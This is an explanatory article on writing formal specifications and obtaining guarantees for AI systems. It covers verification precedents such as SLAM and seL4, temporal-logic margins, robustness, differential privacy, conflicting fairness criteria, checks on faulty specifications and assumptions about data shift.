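# Formal specifications and guarantees for AI systems

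## Formal verification, and what changes when the system is learned

Formal methods are the branch of computer science that deals with writing formal specifications and proving that systems meet them. A *formal specification* describes, in a language with exact mathematical meaning, what a system must or must not do. *Formal verification* ends either in a proof that the system meets the specification in every case the specification covers, or in a *counterexample*, a specific input or run on which the system violates it. Testing gives a weaker guarantee because it checks only the inputs that were tried. A program that reads two 64-bit numbers has 2¹²⁸ possible inputs, so a million tests would cover only a tiny fraction of them.

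Chip makers and software companies have used formal methods for decades. More recently, researchers have been trying to extend them to systems that contain machine-learned models, whose behaviour comes from training on data rather than from instructions a person wrote. Much of the difficulty arises in specifying what to prove.

### The claim and its parts

The basic claim has the form M ⊨ P ("M satisfies P"), where M is the program, or a mathematical model of it, and P is the property.

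For example, when two parts of a program share data, each must acquire a lock before touching the data and release it afterwards, so that they never change the data at the same time. One sensible rule is that acquiring and releasing must strictly alternate. As a specification, this rule is a machine with two states, Unlocked and Locked. Calling "acquire" moves it from Unlocked to Locked, and calling "release" moves it back. Acquiring in the Locked state is an error, and so is releasing in the Unlocked state. P is then the statement that no run of M reaches an error.

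This P is a *safety* property, which means it requires that nothing bad ever happens. If a program violates it, a finite stretch of one run is enough to show this. A *liveness* property requires that something good eventually happens, for example that every part of the program waiting for the lock gets it. No finite stretch of a run can show a violation, because a waiting part might still get the lock one step later. Engineers usually want both kinds of property, because a program that never touches the lock satisfies the alternation rule but does no work.

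Few programs run alone, so the claim often needs a term for the environment. It becomes E, M ⊨ P, or "in the environment E, M satisfies P". E is an *environment model*, a mathematical description of everything outside the system that the proof assumes. If M is a device driver (the program through which an operating system works a printer or a network card), E describes the operating system. The proof gives no assurance if the real environment behaves differently from E, and writing a good E is laborious even for ordinary software. *Pre-QED* (2026), a study of verification by AI agents, argues against the shortcut of reusing as E the code that programmers wrote to test a software library on random inputs. The study instead proposes purpose-built environments, which exposed new bugs even when used only for ordinary testing.

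Most proofs rely on one of two kinds of tool. A *solver* is a program that decides whether a set of logical or arithmetic constraints can all hold at once. If the constraints describe a violation of P and the solver shows that no values satisfy them, there is no violation. A *proof assistant*, such as Lean, Rocq or Isabelle, uses a small core called the kernel to check each step of a proof that someone else has written. Proof assistants can handle a much wider range of properties than automatic tools, but they require much more labour. Either kind of tool may also produce a *certificate*, a record of the result that a separate, simpler program can check.

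A verifier is *sound* if it never reports a false property as proved. It is *complete* if, given enough time, it settles every case as proved or refuted. Soundness alone is easy to achieve, since a program that answers "unknown" to every question is sound.

### What the methods achieved for ordinary software

Driver bugs caused 85% of system crashes in Windows XP, according to Ball, Bounimova and colleagues (2006) in *Thorough Static Analysis of Device Drivers*. To find such bugs, Microsoft researchers built SLAM, a tool that checks drivers against rules like the one above for locks.

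*A Decade of Software Model Checking with SLAM*, a retrospective by the tool's builders, gives the example of a driver that acquires a lock only if a number x is greater than zero and later releases it only if x is greater than zero. SLAM first makes a simplified copy of the program that records only whether the driver holds the lock. Because the copy omits x, it permits a run that skips the acquiring but still does the releasing, which looks like an error. SLAM then checks that run against the real program and finds it impossible, because x would have to be both greater than zero and not greater than zero. It adds the fact "x > 0" to the copy, repeats the analysis, and proves that the error cannot occur. The method works because the copy *over-approximates* the program, meaning that it permits every run of the original and usually some extra ones, so a proof about the copy also holds for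 the program. The method is incomplete because the refinement can in principle go on forever, but in practice SLAM reached a definite answer more than 96% of the time on large classes of drivers.

During the development of Windows 7, Microsoft ran the product version, Static Driver Verifier, after all its other tools, and it still found 270 real bugs in 140 drivers. Of the defects it reported, 90% were real for one family of drivers and 98% for another. People had to supply both E and P. E was a hand-written, much simplified Windows, in which many operating-system functions only returned success or failure arbitrarily. As for P, a senior manager complained early on that it took a Ph.D. to develop the rules, but engineers and interns with no background in verification later wrote or revised about 150 of the 210 or so rules in the 2009 version. Microsoft's *Static Driver Verifier Concepts*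 now lists the tool as unsupported and absent from the Windows 24H2 driver kit, where another analysis tool, CodeQL, replaces it.

SLAM checked narrow rules, whereas Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues (2009), in *seL4*, set out to verify the entire behaviour of a program. They chose a microkernel, the small core of an operating system that runs with unlimited access to the hardware. They wrote an abstract specification of what the kernel does on every call, then used Isabelle to prove that a more detailed design follows the specification and that about 7,500 of the kernel's 8,700 lines of C code follow the design. Under the proof's assumptions, the kernel never crashes or enters an infinite loop, whatever calls a malicious program makes.

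Designing and coding seL4 took 2.2 person-years. The proof took about 20, of which 9 went into tools and libraries that others could reuse and 11 into seL4 itself. Trustworthy Systems, the group behind the kernel, estimates that the proof would fill about 3,500 printed pages. Students' projects and a port to another processor had exposed 16 defects in the C code before verification began in earnest, and verification exposed another 144. Many of these were simple mistakes, but many could crash the kernel or open a security hole. Changing the kernel also took substantial proof work, between 1.5 and 2 person-years for one large batch of new features.

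The 2009 proof assumed that the compiler (which translates C into machine instructions), the hardware, the assembly code and some 1,200 lines of start-up code were correct. These and the specification belong to the *trusted base*, which is all the software, hardware, definitions and human judgements that must be right for a guarantee to hold. Klein and colleagues acknowledge that a cynic might say the code now has precisely the bugs of its specification. They concede the point, but answer that the specification is a third of the size of the code and much simpler to reason about. That is a fair answer for a kernel, because the people who write its specification know what each call should do. Later work shrank the trusted base. In *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*, Klein, Andronick and colleagues report a proof that the kernel's machine code matches the C, so the guarantee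 no longer depends on the compiler.

CompCert is a C compiler with a machine-checked proof that the program it produces behaves as the original does. In *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*, Yang, Chen and colleagues (2011) independently tested it and other compilers by generating random C programs, compiling each with several compilers and comparing the results. Over three years they reported more than 325 bugs, and every compiler they tried produced wrong code without warning at least once. In CompCert they found six such errors in a part that the proof did not cover. Two further faults came from the formal description of the target processor, which left out a limit on the size of a number. After the main developer extended the proof, testing that used about six years of processor time found no wrong code in the newest version. This is unusually direct evidence that a proof prevents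 errors in the parts it covers, and that the remaining faults are concentrated in the trusted base.

For a long time, such proofs were too expensive for anything but small, critical pieces of code. *AI Security Priorities* (2026), a research agenda, predicts that AI coding agents will make verification cheap enough to cover much more of the infrastructure around AI systems, but says it cannot eliminate every risk.

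### When M is a learned model

Making proofs easier to produce does not settle which properties to prove. Jeannette Wing, a computer scientist at Columbia University, took up that question in *Trustworthy AI* (2020) and in a longer version, Wing (2021). Two decades of work on trustworthy computing had produced a list of six properties: reliability, safety, security, privacy, availability and usability. ("Safety" here means that the system does no harm, which is broader and vaguer than the safety property of the lock.) For AI, Wing adds accuracy on new data, robustness to changes in the input, fairness, accountability, transparency, interpretability and the ethical collection and use of data, and leaves the list open. The properties overlap and sometimes conflict. Fairness, for instance, has several reasonable definitions, some of them incompatible. Other properties, such as transparency,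 may have no formal definition at all, and a property can be verified only to the extent that it has been formalised.

The form E, M ⊨ P still fits a self-driving car, where M is the whole car, including its learned vision system, and E is the traffic, roads and pedestrians. Wing gives two reasons why the form is problematic when M is the learned model itself.

One change is that verification has to deal with probability. Engineers can mostly describe an ordinary program as a deterministic machine that moves between discrete states. A learned model takes its inputs from an uncertain world and attaches probabilities to its outputs, and the properties people want from it often concern continuous quantities. For example, differential privacy, which limits how much one person's record can affect a published result, is a bound on a difference between probabilities. The meaning of the symbol ⊨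 therefore changes too, and checking that a model satisfies a property requires reasoning about real numbers, non-linear functions and probability distributions.

Wing goes a little far here in describing the numbers on a neural network's connections as probabilities. They are weights, which can be negative or larger than one. A network with fixed weights ordinarily computes one definite output for each input, which is why proofs about networks are possible. Chance enters through the inputs, training and, in language models, the random choice of each next piece of text.

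Data is the other reason, and in Wing's view perhaps the more significant one. Developers build a model from the data they have in order to use it on data they have not seen. Wing therefore writes the claim as D, M ⊨ P, meaning that the model M satisfies the property P under stated assumptions D about the data. Traditional properties are stated for all inputs, which for an image classifier would include every possible arrangement of pixels, nearly all of them noise with no correct answer. Similarly, a hiring model needs to be fair only for future applicants who resemble those in the training data, in some sense that someone has to define, rather than for every conceivable population. The right assumptions also depend on the task, since a dent in a door matters when inspecting cars at the end of a production line but not when spotting cars on the road.

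Logically, D is an assumption, like E. It deserves its own letter because people obtain it differently. Someone modeling the environment for Windows could consult the people who wrote Windows, but D describes data that nobody has seen yet, so there is no one to ask. Notes from a lecture by Wing (2025) keep the same formula and still list the specification of unseen data among the open problems.

Seshia, Sadigh and Sastry (2017), in *Towards Verified Artificial Intelligence*, divide the obstacles into five challenges. The first is modelling the environment. In rush-hour traffic, nobody may be able to list all the variables that matter or all the ways they can behave, and the over-approximation that worked well for SLAM would produce too many false alarms. The second is specification, since it is unclear how to formally define "recognises a pedestrian". They recommend specifying the whole system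 where possible, for example by requiring that a moving car keep a minimum distance from any object. The third is modelling a component that has thousands of parameters or more and may change as new data arrives. The fourth is building suitable computational engines. Most existing engines give yes-or-no answers, while learned systems need engines that can also reason about quantities and probabilities and generate realistic training and test data. The fifth is design, where they hope to build systems that are correct by construction, so that verification is part of the design process.

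Writing correct specifications remains difficult. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026) surveys 38 studies on verifying plans made by language-model agents, programs in which a language model chooses and carries out actions. When software translates English instructions into formal rules, the rules tend to be well formed but often have the wrong meaning. No approach in the survey was sound, complete, scalable and faithful to the intended meaning without making the agent less useful.

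### The steps of obtaining a guarantee

Anyone who wants a guarantee about an AI system, or has to judge one on offer, faces the same tasks in roughly this order:

1. Write the property as a formal specification, and check that it means what people want.
2. State the assumptions, both about the world (E) and about the data (D).
3. Prove the property of the learned component for every input the assumptions allow. Where no proof is within reach, bound the probability of failure.
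4. Carry the result to the whole system, including the ordinary software around the model. Part of this may be *runtime assurance*, which means watching the system while it runs and switching to a safe fallback before it crosses a specified limit. For a language-model agent it may mean blocking actions that break a rule.
5. Check the trusted base: the tools, the hardware, the definitions and the judgements on which the proof rests.
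6. Compare what the proof establishes with what a law, a regulator or a buyer requires. The usual vehicle is an *assurance case*, a structured argument, with evidence for each step, that the system is acceptable for a stated use.

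## Writing a property as a formal specification

Before anyone can prove that a car does not hit pedestrians, someone has to write that requirement as a formula. The first decision is whether the formula should describe the learned vision component or the whole car.

### The component or the whole system

*SpecRepair* (2021), a paper on correcting faulty networks, defines a property of a network as a set X of inputs and a set Y of outputs, where every input in X must produce an output in Y. For a pedestrian detector, Y is easy to write down as the set of outputs in which "pedestrian" gets the highest score. But X would have to contain every image that shows a pedestrian, including people pushing prams and people half hidden behind a van. Nobody has a formula for that set, which is why developers train a network. Geng, Le and colleagues (2022), in *Towards Reliable Neural Specifications*,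 argue that writing such a specification by hand is no easier than programming a solution to the learning problem directly.

A rule for the whole car, such as "stay at least 2 metres from every obstacle", is about distances. In the environment model E, an obstacle is an object with a position, so the rule doesn't have to describe what a pedestrian looks like. This is why it helps to specify the whole system where possible, as Seshia and colleagues advise. Engineers can then work backwards to the component. If the car needs 30 metres to stop, the vision system has to report an obstacle while it is still at least 32 metres away, and errors about more distant objects do not matter to the rule. Someone still has to relate camera images to positions in E, which is hard, but people can read the top-level requirement and a program can check it.

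*Neuro-Symbolic Verification of Deep Neural Networks* (2022) offers another way to specify a concept that has no formula. Its specification language lets a formula use a second neural network to represent the concept. For example, engineers could require that a car brake whenever the second network detects a pedestrian. The proof relates one network to the other, so it would still hold if both had learned to overlook people in wheelchairs.

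### Behaviour over time

Engineers often write system-level rules in *signal temporal logic*, a language for properties of quantities that change over time. Its smallest formulas compare a number with a threshold, as in d ≥ 2, where d is the distance to the obstacle in metres. Engineers build larger formulas with "and", "or" and "not", and with the operators G ("always"), F ("eventually") and U ("until"), each of which applies over a time interval. The braking rule for a three-second approach is G[0,3](d ≥ 2), which means the distance is at least 2 m at every moment from 0 to 3 seconds.

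A run of the car either satisfies this formula or violates it, but the logic also assigns the run a numerical margin. *Structural-Ambiguity-Aware Translation from Natural Language to Signal Temporal Logic* (Fushimi, Serizawa and colleagues, 2026) sets out the rules for computing it. The margin of d ≥ 2 at one moment is d − 2. "Not" reverses the sign, "and" takes the smaller of two margins, and "or" takes the larger. "Always" takes the minimum over the interval, and "eventually" takes the maximum. The run satisfies the formula if the result is positive and violates it if the result is negative.

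Suppose the car measures distances of 12, 7, 4 and 2.5 m as it brakes. The corresponding margins are 10, 5, 2 and 0.5 m. The formula begins with "always", so the run's margin is the smallest of these, 0.5 m. If the last distance had been 1.5 m, the run's margin would have been −0.5 m.

A yes-or-no verdict would not show how close the car came to failing. As *Model-based Reinforcement Learning from Signal Temporal Logic Specifications* (2020) explains, the margin measures approximately how far a signal can shift before the verdict changes. Here, an error of less than 0.5 m in each reading could not turn the pass into a failure. The margin also helps software search for violations. A test program can vary the car's speed and the road's friction, keeping the changes that shrink the margin until it falls below zero. With only yes-or-no verdicts, the program could not tell which changes brought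 the car closer to failing. A program that designs the braking controller can instead look for changes that increase the margin.

The number reflects only the worst moment that someone sampled. If a formula joins a condition on distance and a condition on speed with "and", it compares metres with kilometres per hour, so the result means little until engineers put both on a common scale. A parked car satisfies the braking rule by a wide margin, so the rule also needs a liveness property beside it, such as "eventually reach the destination".

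Getting from an English sentence to a formula is a further source of error. Fushimi and colleagues discuss the instruction "Within 10 seconds, reach B or reach C while avoiding A". It has two reasonable readings:

- F[0,10] B ∨ (F[0,10] C ∧ G[0,10] ¬A), where the car must avoid A only if it is heading for C;
- F[0,10] (B ∨ C) ∧ G[0,10] ¬A, where it must avoid A in any case.

A route to B that passes through A satisfies the first formula and violates the second. Most translation software picks one reading. The method Fushimi and colleagues propose keeps both and scores how plausible each is, so that a user can look at the routes each would allow and choose a reading.

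### Robustness of a classifier

Sometimes engineers do need a property of the component itself, and the usual choice for a classifier is *local robustness*. It requires that small changes to one input x, such as a photograph that a person has labelled, leave the predicted class unchanged. Formally, the network is ε-robust at x if it assigns the same class to every x′ with ‖x′ − x‖∞ ≤ ε. The distance ‖x′ − x‖∞ is the largest change to any single pixel. If brightness runs from 0 to 1 and ε = 0.1, all the pixels may change at once, each by up to 0.1. In the general form above, X is the set of images within ε of x, and Y is the set of outputs that give x's class the highest score. The specification doesn't need a definition of "pedestrian", because it relies on a person having recognised one in x.

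However, the property covers only inputs near x. Geng and colleagues show how small this region can be on MNIST, a standard collection of handwritten digits. They take a training image of a 1 and find an altered version, at a distance of 0.2, that the network classifies as an 8. The network can therefore be robust around that image only for ε below 0.2. An ordinary 1 from the test set, whose closest training image is this one, lies much further away. They could verify none of the unseen test images when they used the neighbourhoods of all the training images as the specification.

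Their alternative is to specify a pattern of active and inactive neurons that images of the same digit tend to share, then prove that every input with that pattern gets the right label. Such patterns covered up to 84% of the test images. However, the patterns come from the network being verified, so the specification depends on how that network already recognizes digits. In the loosest version, 967 of the 980 test images of a 0 matched the pattern for 0, but so did 20 images of other digits.

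The distance between two images' pixel values is also a poor measure of their similarity. Cropping a photograph changes nearly every pixel but may not change anything that matters. Wing would like proofs to cover "semantic" changes such as rotating or darkening an image. The problem is worse for text, since replacing one word may preserve the meaning of a sentence or reverse it.

### Differential privacy

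Differential privacy is a property of the training procedure rather than of a finished model. Call two datasets neighbours if one contains a single record that the other lacks. In the form that *Towards TEE-Certified DP* (2026) gives, a randomised training algorithm A is (ε, δ)-differentially private if, for all neighbouring datasets T and T′ and every set S of possible results,

Pr[A(T) ∈ S] ≤ e^ε · Pr[A(T′) ∈ S] + δ.

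(This ε is unrelated to the one in local robustness.) If ε and δ are small, training gives nearly the same distribution of results with or without any one record, so studying the model reveals little about whether that record was in the training data.

*VaultGemma* (2025) describes a Google language model with one billion parameters that has this guarantee for all of its initial training, with ε ≤ 2 and δ ≤ 1.1 × 10⁻¹⁰. Ignoring the tiny δ, this means that adding one record can make any result at most e², or about 7.4, times as probable. A record here is a sequence of 1,024 tokens (short pieces of text). Some documents appear several times in the training data, and each copy counts as a separate record, so the guarantee is weaker for a secret that appears in many sequences. In a test on about a million training samples, the team gave the model 50 tokens and checked whether it continued with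 the next 50. They detected no memorisation, whereas all the Gemma models in the comparison that lacked the guarantee showed some. The guarantee substantially reduced the model's usefulness, to a level comparable to that of non-private models from about five years before.

The specification includes the values of ε and δ and the definition of a record, and "trained with differential privacy" means little without them. NIST, the US standards agency, has published *Guidelines for Evaluating Differential Privacy Guarantees* to help organisations judge such claims, such as a vendor's promise that nobody can re-identify a person in a database.

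### Fairness, and properties that conflict

COMPAS is a commercial score that US courts use to estimate whether a defendant will reoffend. The news organisation ProPublica found that it labelled black defendants who did not reoffend as high-risk nearly twice as often as white defendants who did not reoffend. Northpointe, the company behind COMPAS, answered that a high-risk label meant the same thing in both groups, since about the same share of high-risk defendants in each group reoffended. *Fair prediction with disparate impact* (Chouldechova, 2017) shows that both were right, because they used different definitions of fairness.

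| Criterion | What has to be equal in the two groups |
|---|---|
| Statistical parity | The share of people with a high-risk label |
| Calibration | At each value of the score, the share who reoffend |
| Predictive parity | Among people with a high-risk label, the share who reoffend (the precision) |
| Error rate balance | The share of non-reoffenders with a high-risk label (the false-positive rate) and the share of reoffenders without one (the miss rate) |

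If p is the share of a group that reoffends, its base rate, then simple counting gives

false-positive rate = p/(1 − p) × (1 − precision)/precision × (1 − miss rate).

Suppose a high-risk label has a precision of 80% and a miss rate of 20% in each of two groups of 1,000 people. In the first group the base rate is 50%, so 500 people reoffend and 400 of them have the label. Those 400 are 80% of everyone with the label, so another 100 people have it wrongly. Since 500 people do not reoffend, the false-positive rate is 20%. In the second group the base rate is 20%, so 200 people reoffend and 160 of them have the label. Another 40 people have it wrongly, out of the 800 who do not reoffend, so the false-positive rate is 5%.

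If base rates differ between groups, any algorithm with equal precision for each group must have unequal error rates, unless it predicts perfectly. In the COMPAS data, the base rates were 51% for black defendants and 39% for white defendants. With equal precision and equal miss rates, the formula gives a false-positive rate about 1.6 times as high for black defendants. The real gap was larger because the miss rates also differed.

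Someone therefore has to choose a criterion, and the choice depends on the use. Chouldechova considers statistical parity well suited to hiring and admissions but hard to justify for predicting crime. She also stresses that fairness is a social and ethical concept, not a statistical one, and that an instrument that meets a criterion can still harm a group disproportionately, depending on how courts use it. Proving that COMPAS satisfied predictive parity would not have settled the dispute over it.

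Other conflicts between properties are found by experiment rather than proved mathematically. In *The Privacy-Hallucination Tradeoff in Differentially Private Language Models*, Ramesh, Pruthi and colleagues (2026) further trained a language model on Wikipedia articles newer than its original data, with and without differential privacy, and then had it write articles on the same topics. For topics in AI, an automatic checker rated 37.7% of the claims correct without privacy, 33.8% at ε = 16 and 31.6% at the stricter ε = 8. The first drop was not statistically significant, but the second was, and human raters also found more unsupported claims with privacy at ε = 16. The noise added for privacy spreads the model's probability over more possible next words, including wrong ones. Better training methods might reduce this conflict, but they can't reduce the one between fairness criteria.

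### Properties with no formula

Ethical use, like transparency, may never have a formula, which for Wing limits how far verification of AI can reach. She suggests that law, policy and social norms could supply a context in which a narrower question has a formal answer. "Did the developers collect the data ethically?" has no formula, but "does every record have a signed consent form?" does. (Turning legal rules into formulas has difficulties of its own.)

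Harm in open conversation may be the hardest property to specify. The same paragraph on the maximum dose of a painkiller helps a nurse and may endanger a person in despair. Because the harm depends on the reader, no formula about the text alone can capture it. Developers can ban particular phrases, which catches little, or train a classifier to recognise harm and require that it never flag the system's output. The classifier then has the same role as the second network in the pedestrian example, and a proof would be only as reliable as the classifier.

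Fedorin (2026), in *So You Want to Build a Mainstream Formally Verifiable Language*, argues more generally that whether a specification fits its purpose depends on the outside world, so a better programming language can do little to ensure that it does. *Intent Formalization* (2026), on AI-written code, agrees that only the user can say whether a specification is right, but is more hopeful that tools can help users find out. This limit matters less for emergency brakes, where a distance rule covers much of what people want, than for a general-purpose chatbot, for which no comparable rule exists.

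### Testing a specification before proving anything

A wrong formula can look right even to experts. Dokhanchi, Hoxha and Fainekos (2016), in *Formal Requirement Elicitation and Debugging for Testing and Verification of Cyber-Physical Systems*, asked people to formalise the requirement that, at some time in the first 30 seconds, a vehicle's speed v goes over 100 and stays there for 20 seconds. One person with a background in formal logic wrote

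F[0,30]((v > 100) ⇒ G[0,20](v > 100)).

Every possible run satisfies this formula. If the speed is 100 or less at any moment in the first 30 seconds, the "if" part is false at that moment, which makes the implication true. If the speed is above 100 throughout, it is also above 100 for the first 20 seconds. Writing "and" instead of "implies" fixes the formula. A solver can find such errors without any information about the vehicle, by checking whether any run could violate the formula and whether any could satisfy it.

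A related fault is *vacuity*, where part of a formula has no effect. To detect it, software replaces that part with "false" and checks whether the original formula implies the altered one. Dokhanchi and colleagues ran three automatic checks on 87 formulas that people had produced with a graphical tool. The checks found five formulas that were always true or always false, nine that contained a redundant requirement, and five that were vacuous. The other 68 passed, though some may still not have expressed what their writers intended. The checks can be slow. One formula took 11 hours, and *A Tree-Shaped Tableau for Checking the Satisfiability of Signal Temporal Logic* (2025) lists efficiently checking whole sets of requirements for consistency as an open problem.

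Some vacuity shows up only when the system runs. The rule "whenever an obstacle is within 30 m, the brakes come on within a second" holds on every drive along an empty road. Testers should therefore record whether the "whenever" condition was ever met, and disregard runs where it wasn't.

Logical checks cannot reveal that a formula is too weak, but engineers can test for this by trying it on systems they have deliberately broken, such as a simulated car whose brakes respond a second late. If the broken car passes, the specification needs revision. *Spec-Harness* (2026) gives an example in which a language model specified a small program that swaps the case of a letter and leaves other characters alone. The verifier confirmed that the program met the specification, but the specification required only that a lower-case letter become some capital letter, so a program that turned every letter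 into Q would have met it too. The specification also excluded inputs such as "+", which the program handles correctly. The same verifier accepted an empty specification. A score based on altered versions of the program separated the candidates, giving 0.09 to the empty specification, 0.36 to the model's and 0.94 to an exact one, but it did not show what to fix.

Others test the specification directly on inputs and outputs. *SpecRL* (2026) supplies plausible wrong outputs, such as numbers that are off by one, and counts how many the specification rejects. *Verus-SpecGym* (2026) uses inputs that competitors in programming contests devised to break each other's solutions. Having another language model review the specification is less reliable. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) cites a study in which language model judges missed a quarter of the faulty specifications.

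One remaining check is to restate the formula in plain words and ask people whether it is what they want, but the evidence for this is discouraging. Siu, Leahy and Mann (2023), in *STL*, showed 62 people formulas that constrained a robot's moves in a game of capture the flag and asked whether every plan that obeyed the formula would win. There were three possible answers, and people were right 45% of the time. They tended to approve formulas, so they did well on valid ones and badly on those that allowed the robot to lose. They were also about as confident when wrong as when right. Familiarity with formal methods helped somewhat, but replacing the symbols with English did not make a significant difference. This is probably because most of the difficulty lies in working out everything a formula permits, which readers of a word-for-word translation still have to do. Showing people specific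 runs that the formula allows, as Fushimi and colleagues suggest for ambiguous instructions, addresses that difficulty more directly, although Siu and colleagues did not test it.

### The Salt method

*AI with Authority, from Application to Silicon* (Hickey, 2026) describes Salt, a working method that combines several of these checks. Hickey directed a small group of AI agents that wrote mathematics, software and a processor design, with proofs in Lean. Hickey never reviewed a proof. The human's only jobs were to say what was wanted and to read the statements the agents proved.

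Work begins with an objective in prose. Agents challenge it by looking for contradictions, gaps and missing cases, then interview the human to settle the open points. The result is a set of prose requirements with success criteria that nobody may change later. All this happens before any code exists, because a specification written afterwards tends to describe whatever the code does. Agents may not weaken a statement to make it easier to prove. Tolmach and Klaus warn that an agent rewarded for finishing proofs has an incentive to do this. They also warn of theorems whose assumptions nothing can satisfy.

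The agents then deliver five things: the implementation, the specification, a proof that the implementation satisfies the specification, tests, and a restatement of the specification in simpler terms. The tests include controls that must be able to fail. The restatement comes with its own proof that the specification implies it, so it may be weaker than what the agents proved but never stronger. This improves on an informal paraphrase, which can overstate. The restatement could still be so weak that it is trivial, so someone has to read it critically.

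The project produced over 320,000 lines of Lean in 37 days, and Hickey reports that no incorrect proof entered the record. The Lean kernel rejects incorrect proofs, so their absence is not evidence that the statements were right. The numbering in the project's error log reached 256 in two weeks, and the entries included claims with the wrong scope and mistakes in the statements themselves. Only 288 of the 902 one-bit memory cells in the processor design first submitted for manufacture came from parts that Lean had checked. Hickey is a specialist in formal methods who worked alone, and the study has no comparison group, so it cannot show how much each check contributed or whether other people would do as well.

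## Stating what is assumed about the data and the world

A proof that a car keeps 2 metres from every obstacle holds only under conditions such as working brakes, a dry road and pedestrians who stay below some speed. These conditions are part of the guarantee, and engineers need to write them precisely enough that someone could find out if they are false. For example, "less than 5 mm of rain an hour, and no pedestrian faster than 3 metres per second" can be checked, while "normal driving conditions" is too vague.

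### Wing's questions about unseen data

Traditional properties are stated for all inputs. For learned models, Wing suggests stating them for all distributions of data instead. A distribution describes how often each kind of input occurs. This suits accuracy and fairness, which are properties of a model's results over many inputs. But such a property can't be expected to hold for every possible distribution, since one of them contains only the inputs that the model gets wrong. It should hold for the distributions that real-world phenomena produce, and someone has to specify which ones those are.

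Specifying even one distribution can be difficult. The mean and variance are enough for data that follow a bell curve. For more complicated data, Wing suggests starting from probabilistic programming languages such as Stan, in which a program describes a random process that generates inputs. It is unclear how to do this for large real-world datasets that fit no common statistical model.

Wing then asks how anyone can trust the specification of D. Developers built M on the assumption that future data would resemble the training data. If they write the same assumption into D, the proof assumes what users are worried about. Wing compares this with ordinary verification, where engineers provisionally accept E and P and revise them when they find a problem. To avoid this circularity, she proposes checking D by other means, such as statistical tests, or starting with a D simple enough for a person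 to inspect and refining it repeatedly, much as SLAM refined its simplified copy of a driver. Each round may change D, M or P.

Suppose a hiring model misjudges 2% of applicants with conventional careers and 10% of career changers. Career changers make up 20% of the training data, so the overall error rate is 3.6%. In the first version of D, the developers assume that this share will stay at 20%. The next year it rises to 30%, so the assumption is false. The developers widen D to allow any share up to 40%, but still assume that applicants in each group resemble that group's training data. The worst-case error rate is then 0.6 × 2% + 0.4 × 10% = 5.2%. If P requires an error rate below 5%, the proof fails, and the developers have to improve M for career changers, relax P or justify a narrower D.

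The statistical check showed that this year's applicants did not match the specification, but such a check can only refute D. Even if they had matched, next year's applicants might not.

### What a shift in the data costs

Suppose engineers have shown that a system fails with probability at most 0.0001 on inputs from D, and the real inputs come from a slightly different distribution D′. A common measure of the difference is the *total variation distance*, the largest gap between the probabilities that the two distributions give to the same set of inputs:

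TV(D, D′) = max over all sets A of |D(A) − D′(A)|.

The inputs on which the system fails are one such set. Call it F. Its probability under D′ can exceed its probability under D by at most the distance, so

D′(F) ≤ D(F) + TV(D, D′).

If the distance is 0.01, the bound becomes 0.0001 + 0.01 = 0.0101. A system meant to fail at most once in 10,000 times may now fail about once in 99.

This can happen if 1% of the new images show snow, D contained no snow, and the vision system fails on every snowy image. The failure probability is then 0.99 × 0.0001 + 0.01, or about 0.0101. Improving the system on D would hardly help, since the bound would be 0.01 even if it never failed there. To keep the bound within twice its original value, the distance must be no more than 0.0001. A new kind of input that makes up one in 10,000 would already reach that limit, and it would take about 30,000 inputs to have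 a 95% chance of seeing even one example.

Assumptions about total variation distance are hard to justify. *Fair Classification with Adversarial Perturbations* (2021) describes a fairness method that assumes a known distance between the true and corrupted data for each protected group, but in most applications nobody knows that distance.

Engineers can get a tighter bound if they know how the data will change. When the share of career changers rises from 20% to 40%, the total variation distance may be as large as 0.2, so the general formula allows an error rate of up to 23.6%. The earlier calculation gave 5.2% because it also assumed that each group stayed the same internally, which people can check separately. Engineers can also prove the property for every input in a set, such as all images within a given range of brightness. Shifts within the set then don't increase the error bound, and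 engineers only have to add the probability of an input from outside it.

### Fairness over a class of distributions

A fairness result for one dataset may not hold when the mix of people changes. Mandal, Deng and colleagues (2020) show this with the COMPAS data in *Ensuring Fairness Beyond the Training Data*. They used an existing method to train a classifier close to statistical parity, with rates of positive predictions for black and white defendants that differed by at most 0.02. They then reweighted the records, as if certain kinds of defendant had become more common, and the gap rose to at least 0.2. The distribution of each feature, taken separately, looked almost the same as before, so checking the features one at a time would not have revealed the change.

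Wing asks what a counterexample would be for a learned model, and here it is a set of weights. The worst set is awkward to find because each group's rate is a fraction with weights in both the numerator and the denominator. Mandal and colleagues fix the total weight of each group, which turns the problem into a linear program, a type of optimisation problem that standard software solves efficiently. They repeat this for a grid of possible totals.

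Their training method is a game between two programs. One proposes a classifier, and the other looks for the weights that make it most unfair. That unfairness is then a penalty when the first program chooses its next classifier. After enough rounds, the method outputs a random mixture of all the proposed classifiers. An outer loop plays a similar game over accuracy, using the weights that make the classifier's weighted error largest. They prove that if the developer sets a target gap g, the mixture's gap is at most 2g for every set of weights in the class.

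In the theory, the class contains every possible weighting of the training records, which is too broad for statistical parity. A weighting could put all the weight on two people, one in the first group with a positive prediction and one in the second with a negative prediction. The gap between the groups' positive prediction rates would then be 1, so only a classifier that treats nearly everyone alike could pass. The experiments measured fairness over a narrower class, where each record's weight could change only by a limited percentage and each group's total stayed fixed. They used four datasets of about 2,000 records each, covering incomes, crime, law exams and COMPAS. On most of them, unfairness grew more slowly than with earlier methods as the permitted change increased. In exchange, accuracy on the original distribution fell by at most 5–10%.

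Reweighting the training examples also cannot represent a kind of person who is missing from them. Mandal and colleagues leave broader classes of distributions to future work.

### Guaranteed safe AI

When a system acts on the world, its actions change the data it later receives. A company might test a self-driving car for a million miles without an accident, but human drivers who get used to such cars may become more aggressive around them. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) uses this example to argue that testing alone cannot justify high confidence in advanced AI. It proposes that such systems come with a quantitative guarantee built from three parts.

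The first is a *world model*, their name for an environment model. It takes a state of the world and an action, and returns the possible next states and observations with their probabilities. Where nobody can justify a single set of probabilities, it may return several sets. The *safety specification* assigns a number between 0 and 1 to an AI system in a world model, such as the probability of a collision within an hour. The *verifier* computes or bounds that number and produces evidence that others can check. The AI system qualifies if the number falls within a permitted range.

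(In most current AI research, "world model" means something else, an AI system's internal representation of its surroundings. Zou (2026), in *What Today's "World Models" Can and Cannot Tell Us About Safety*, uses it in this sense. The verifier's model can be entirely separate from any model inside the AI.)

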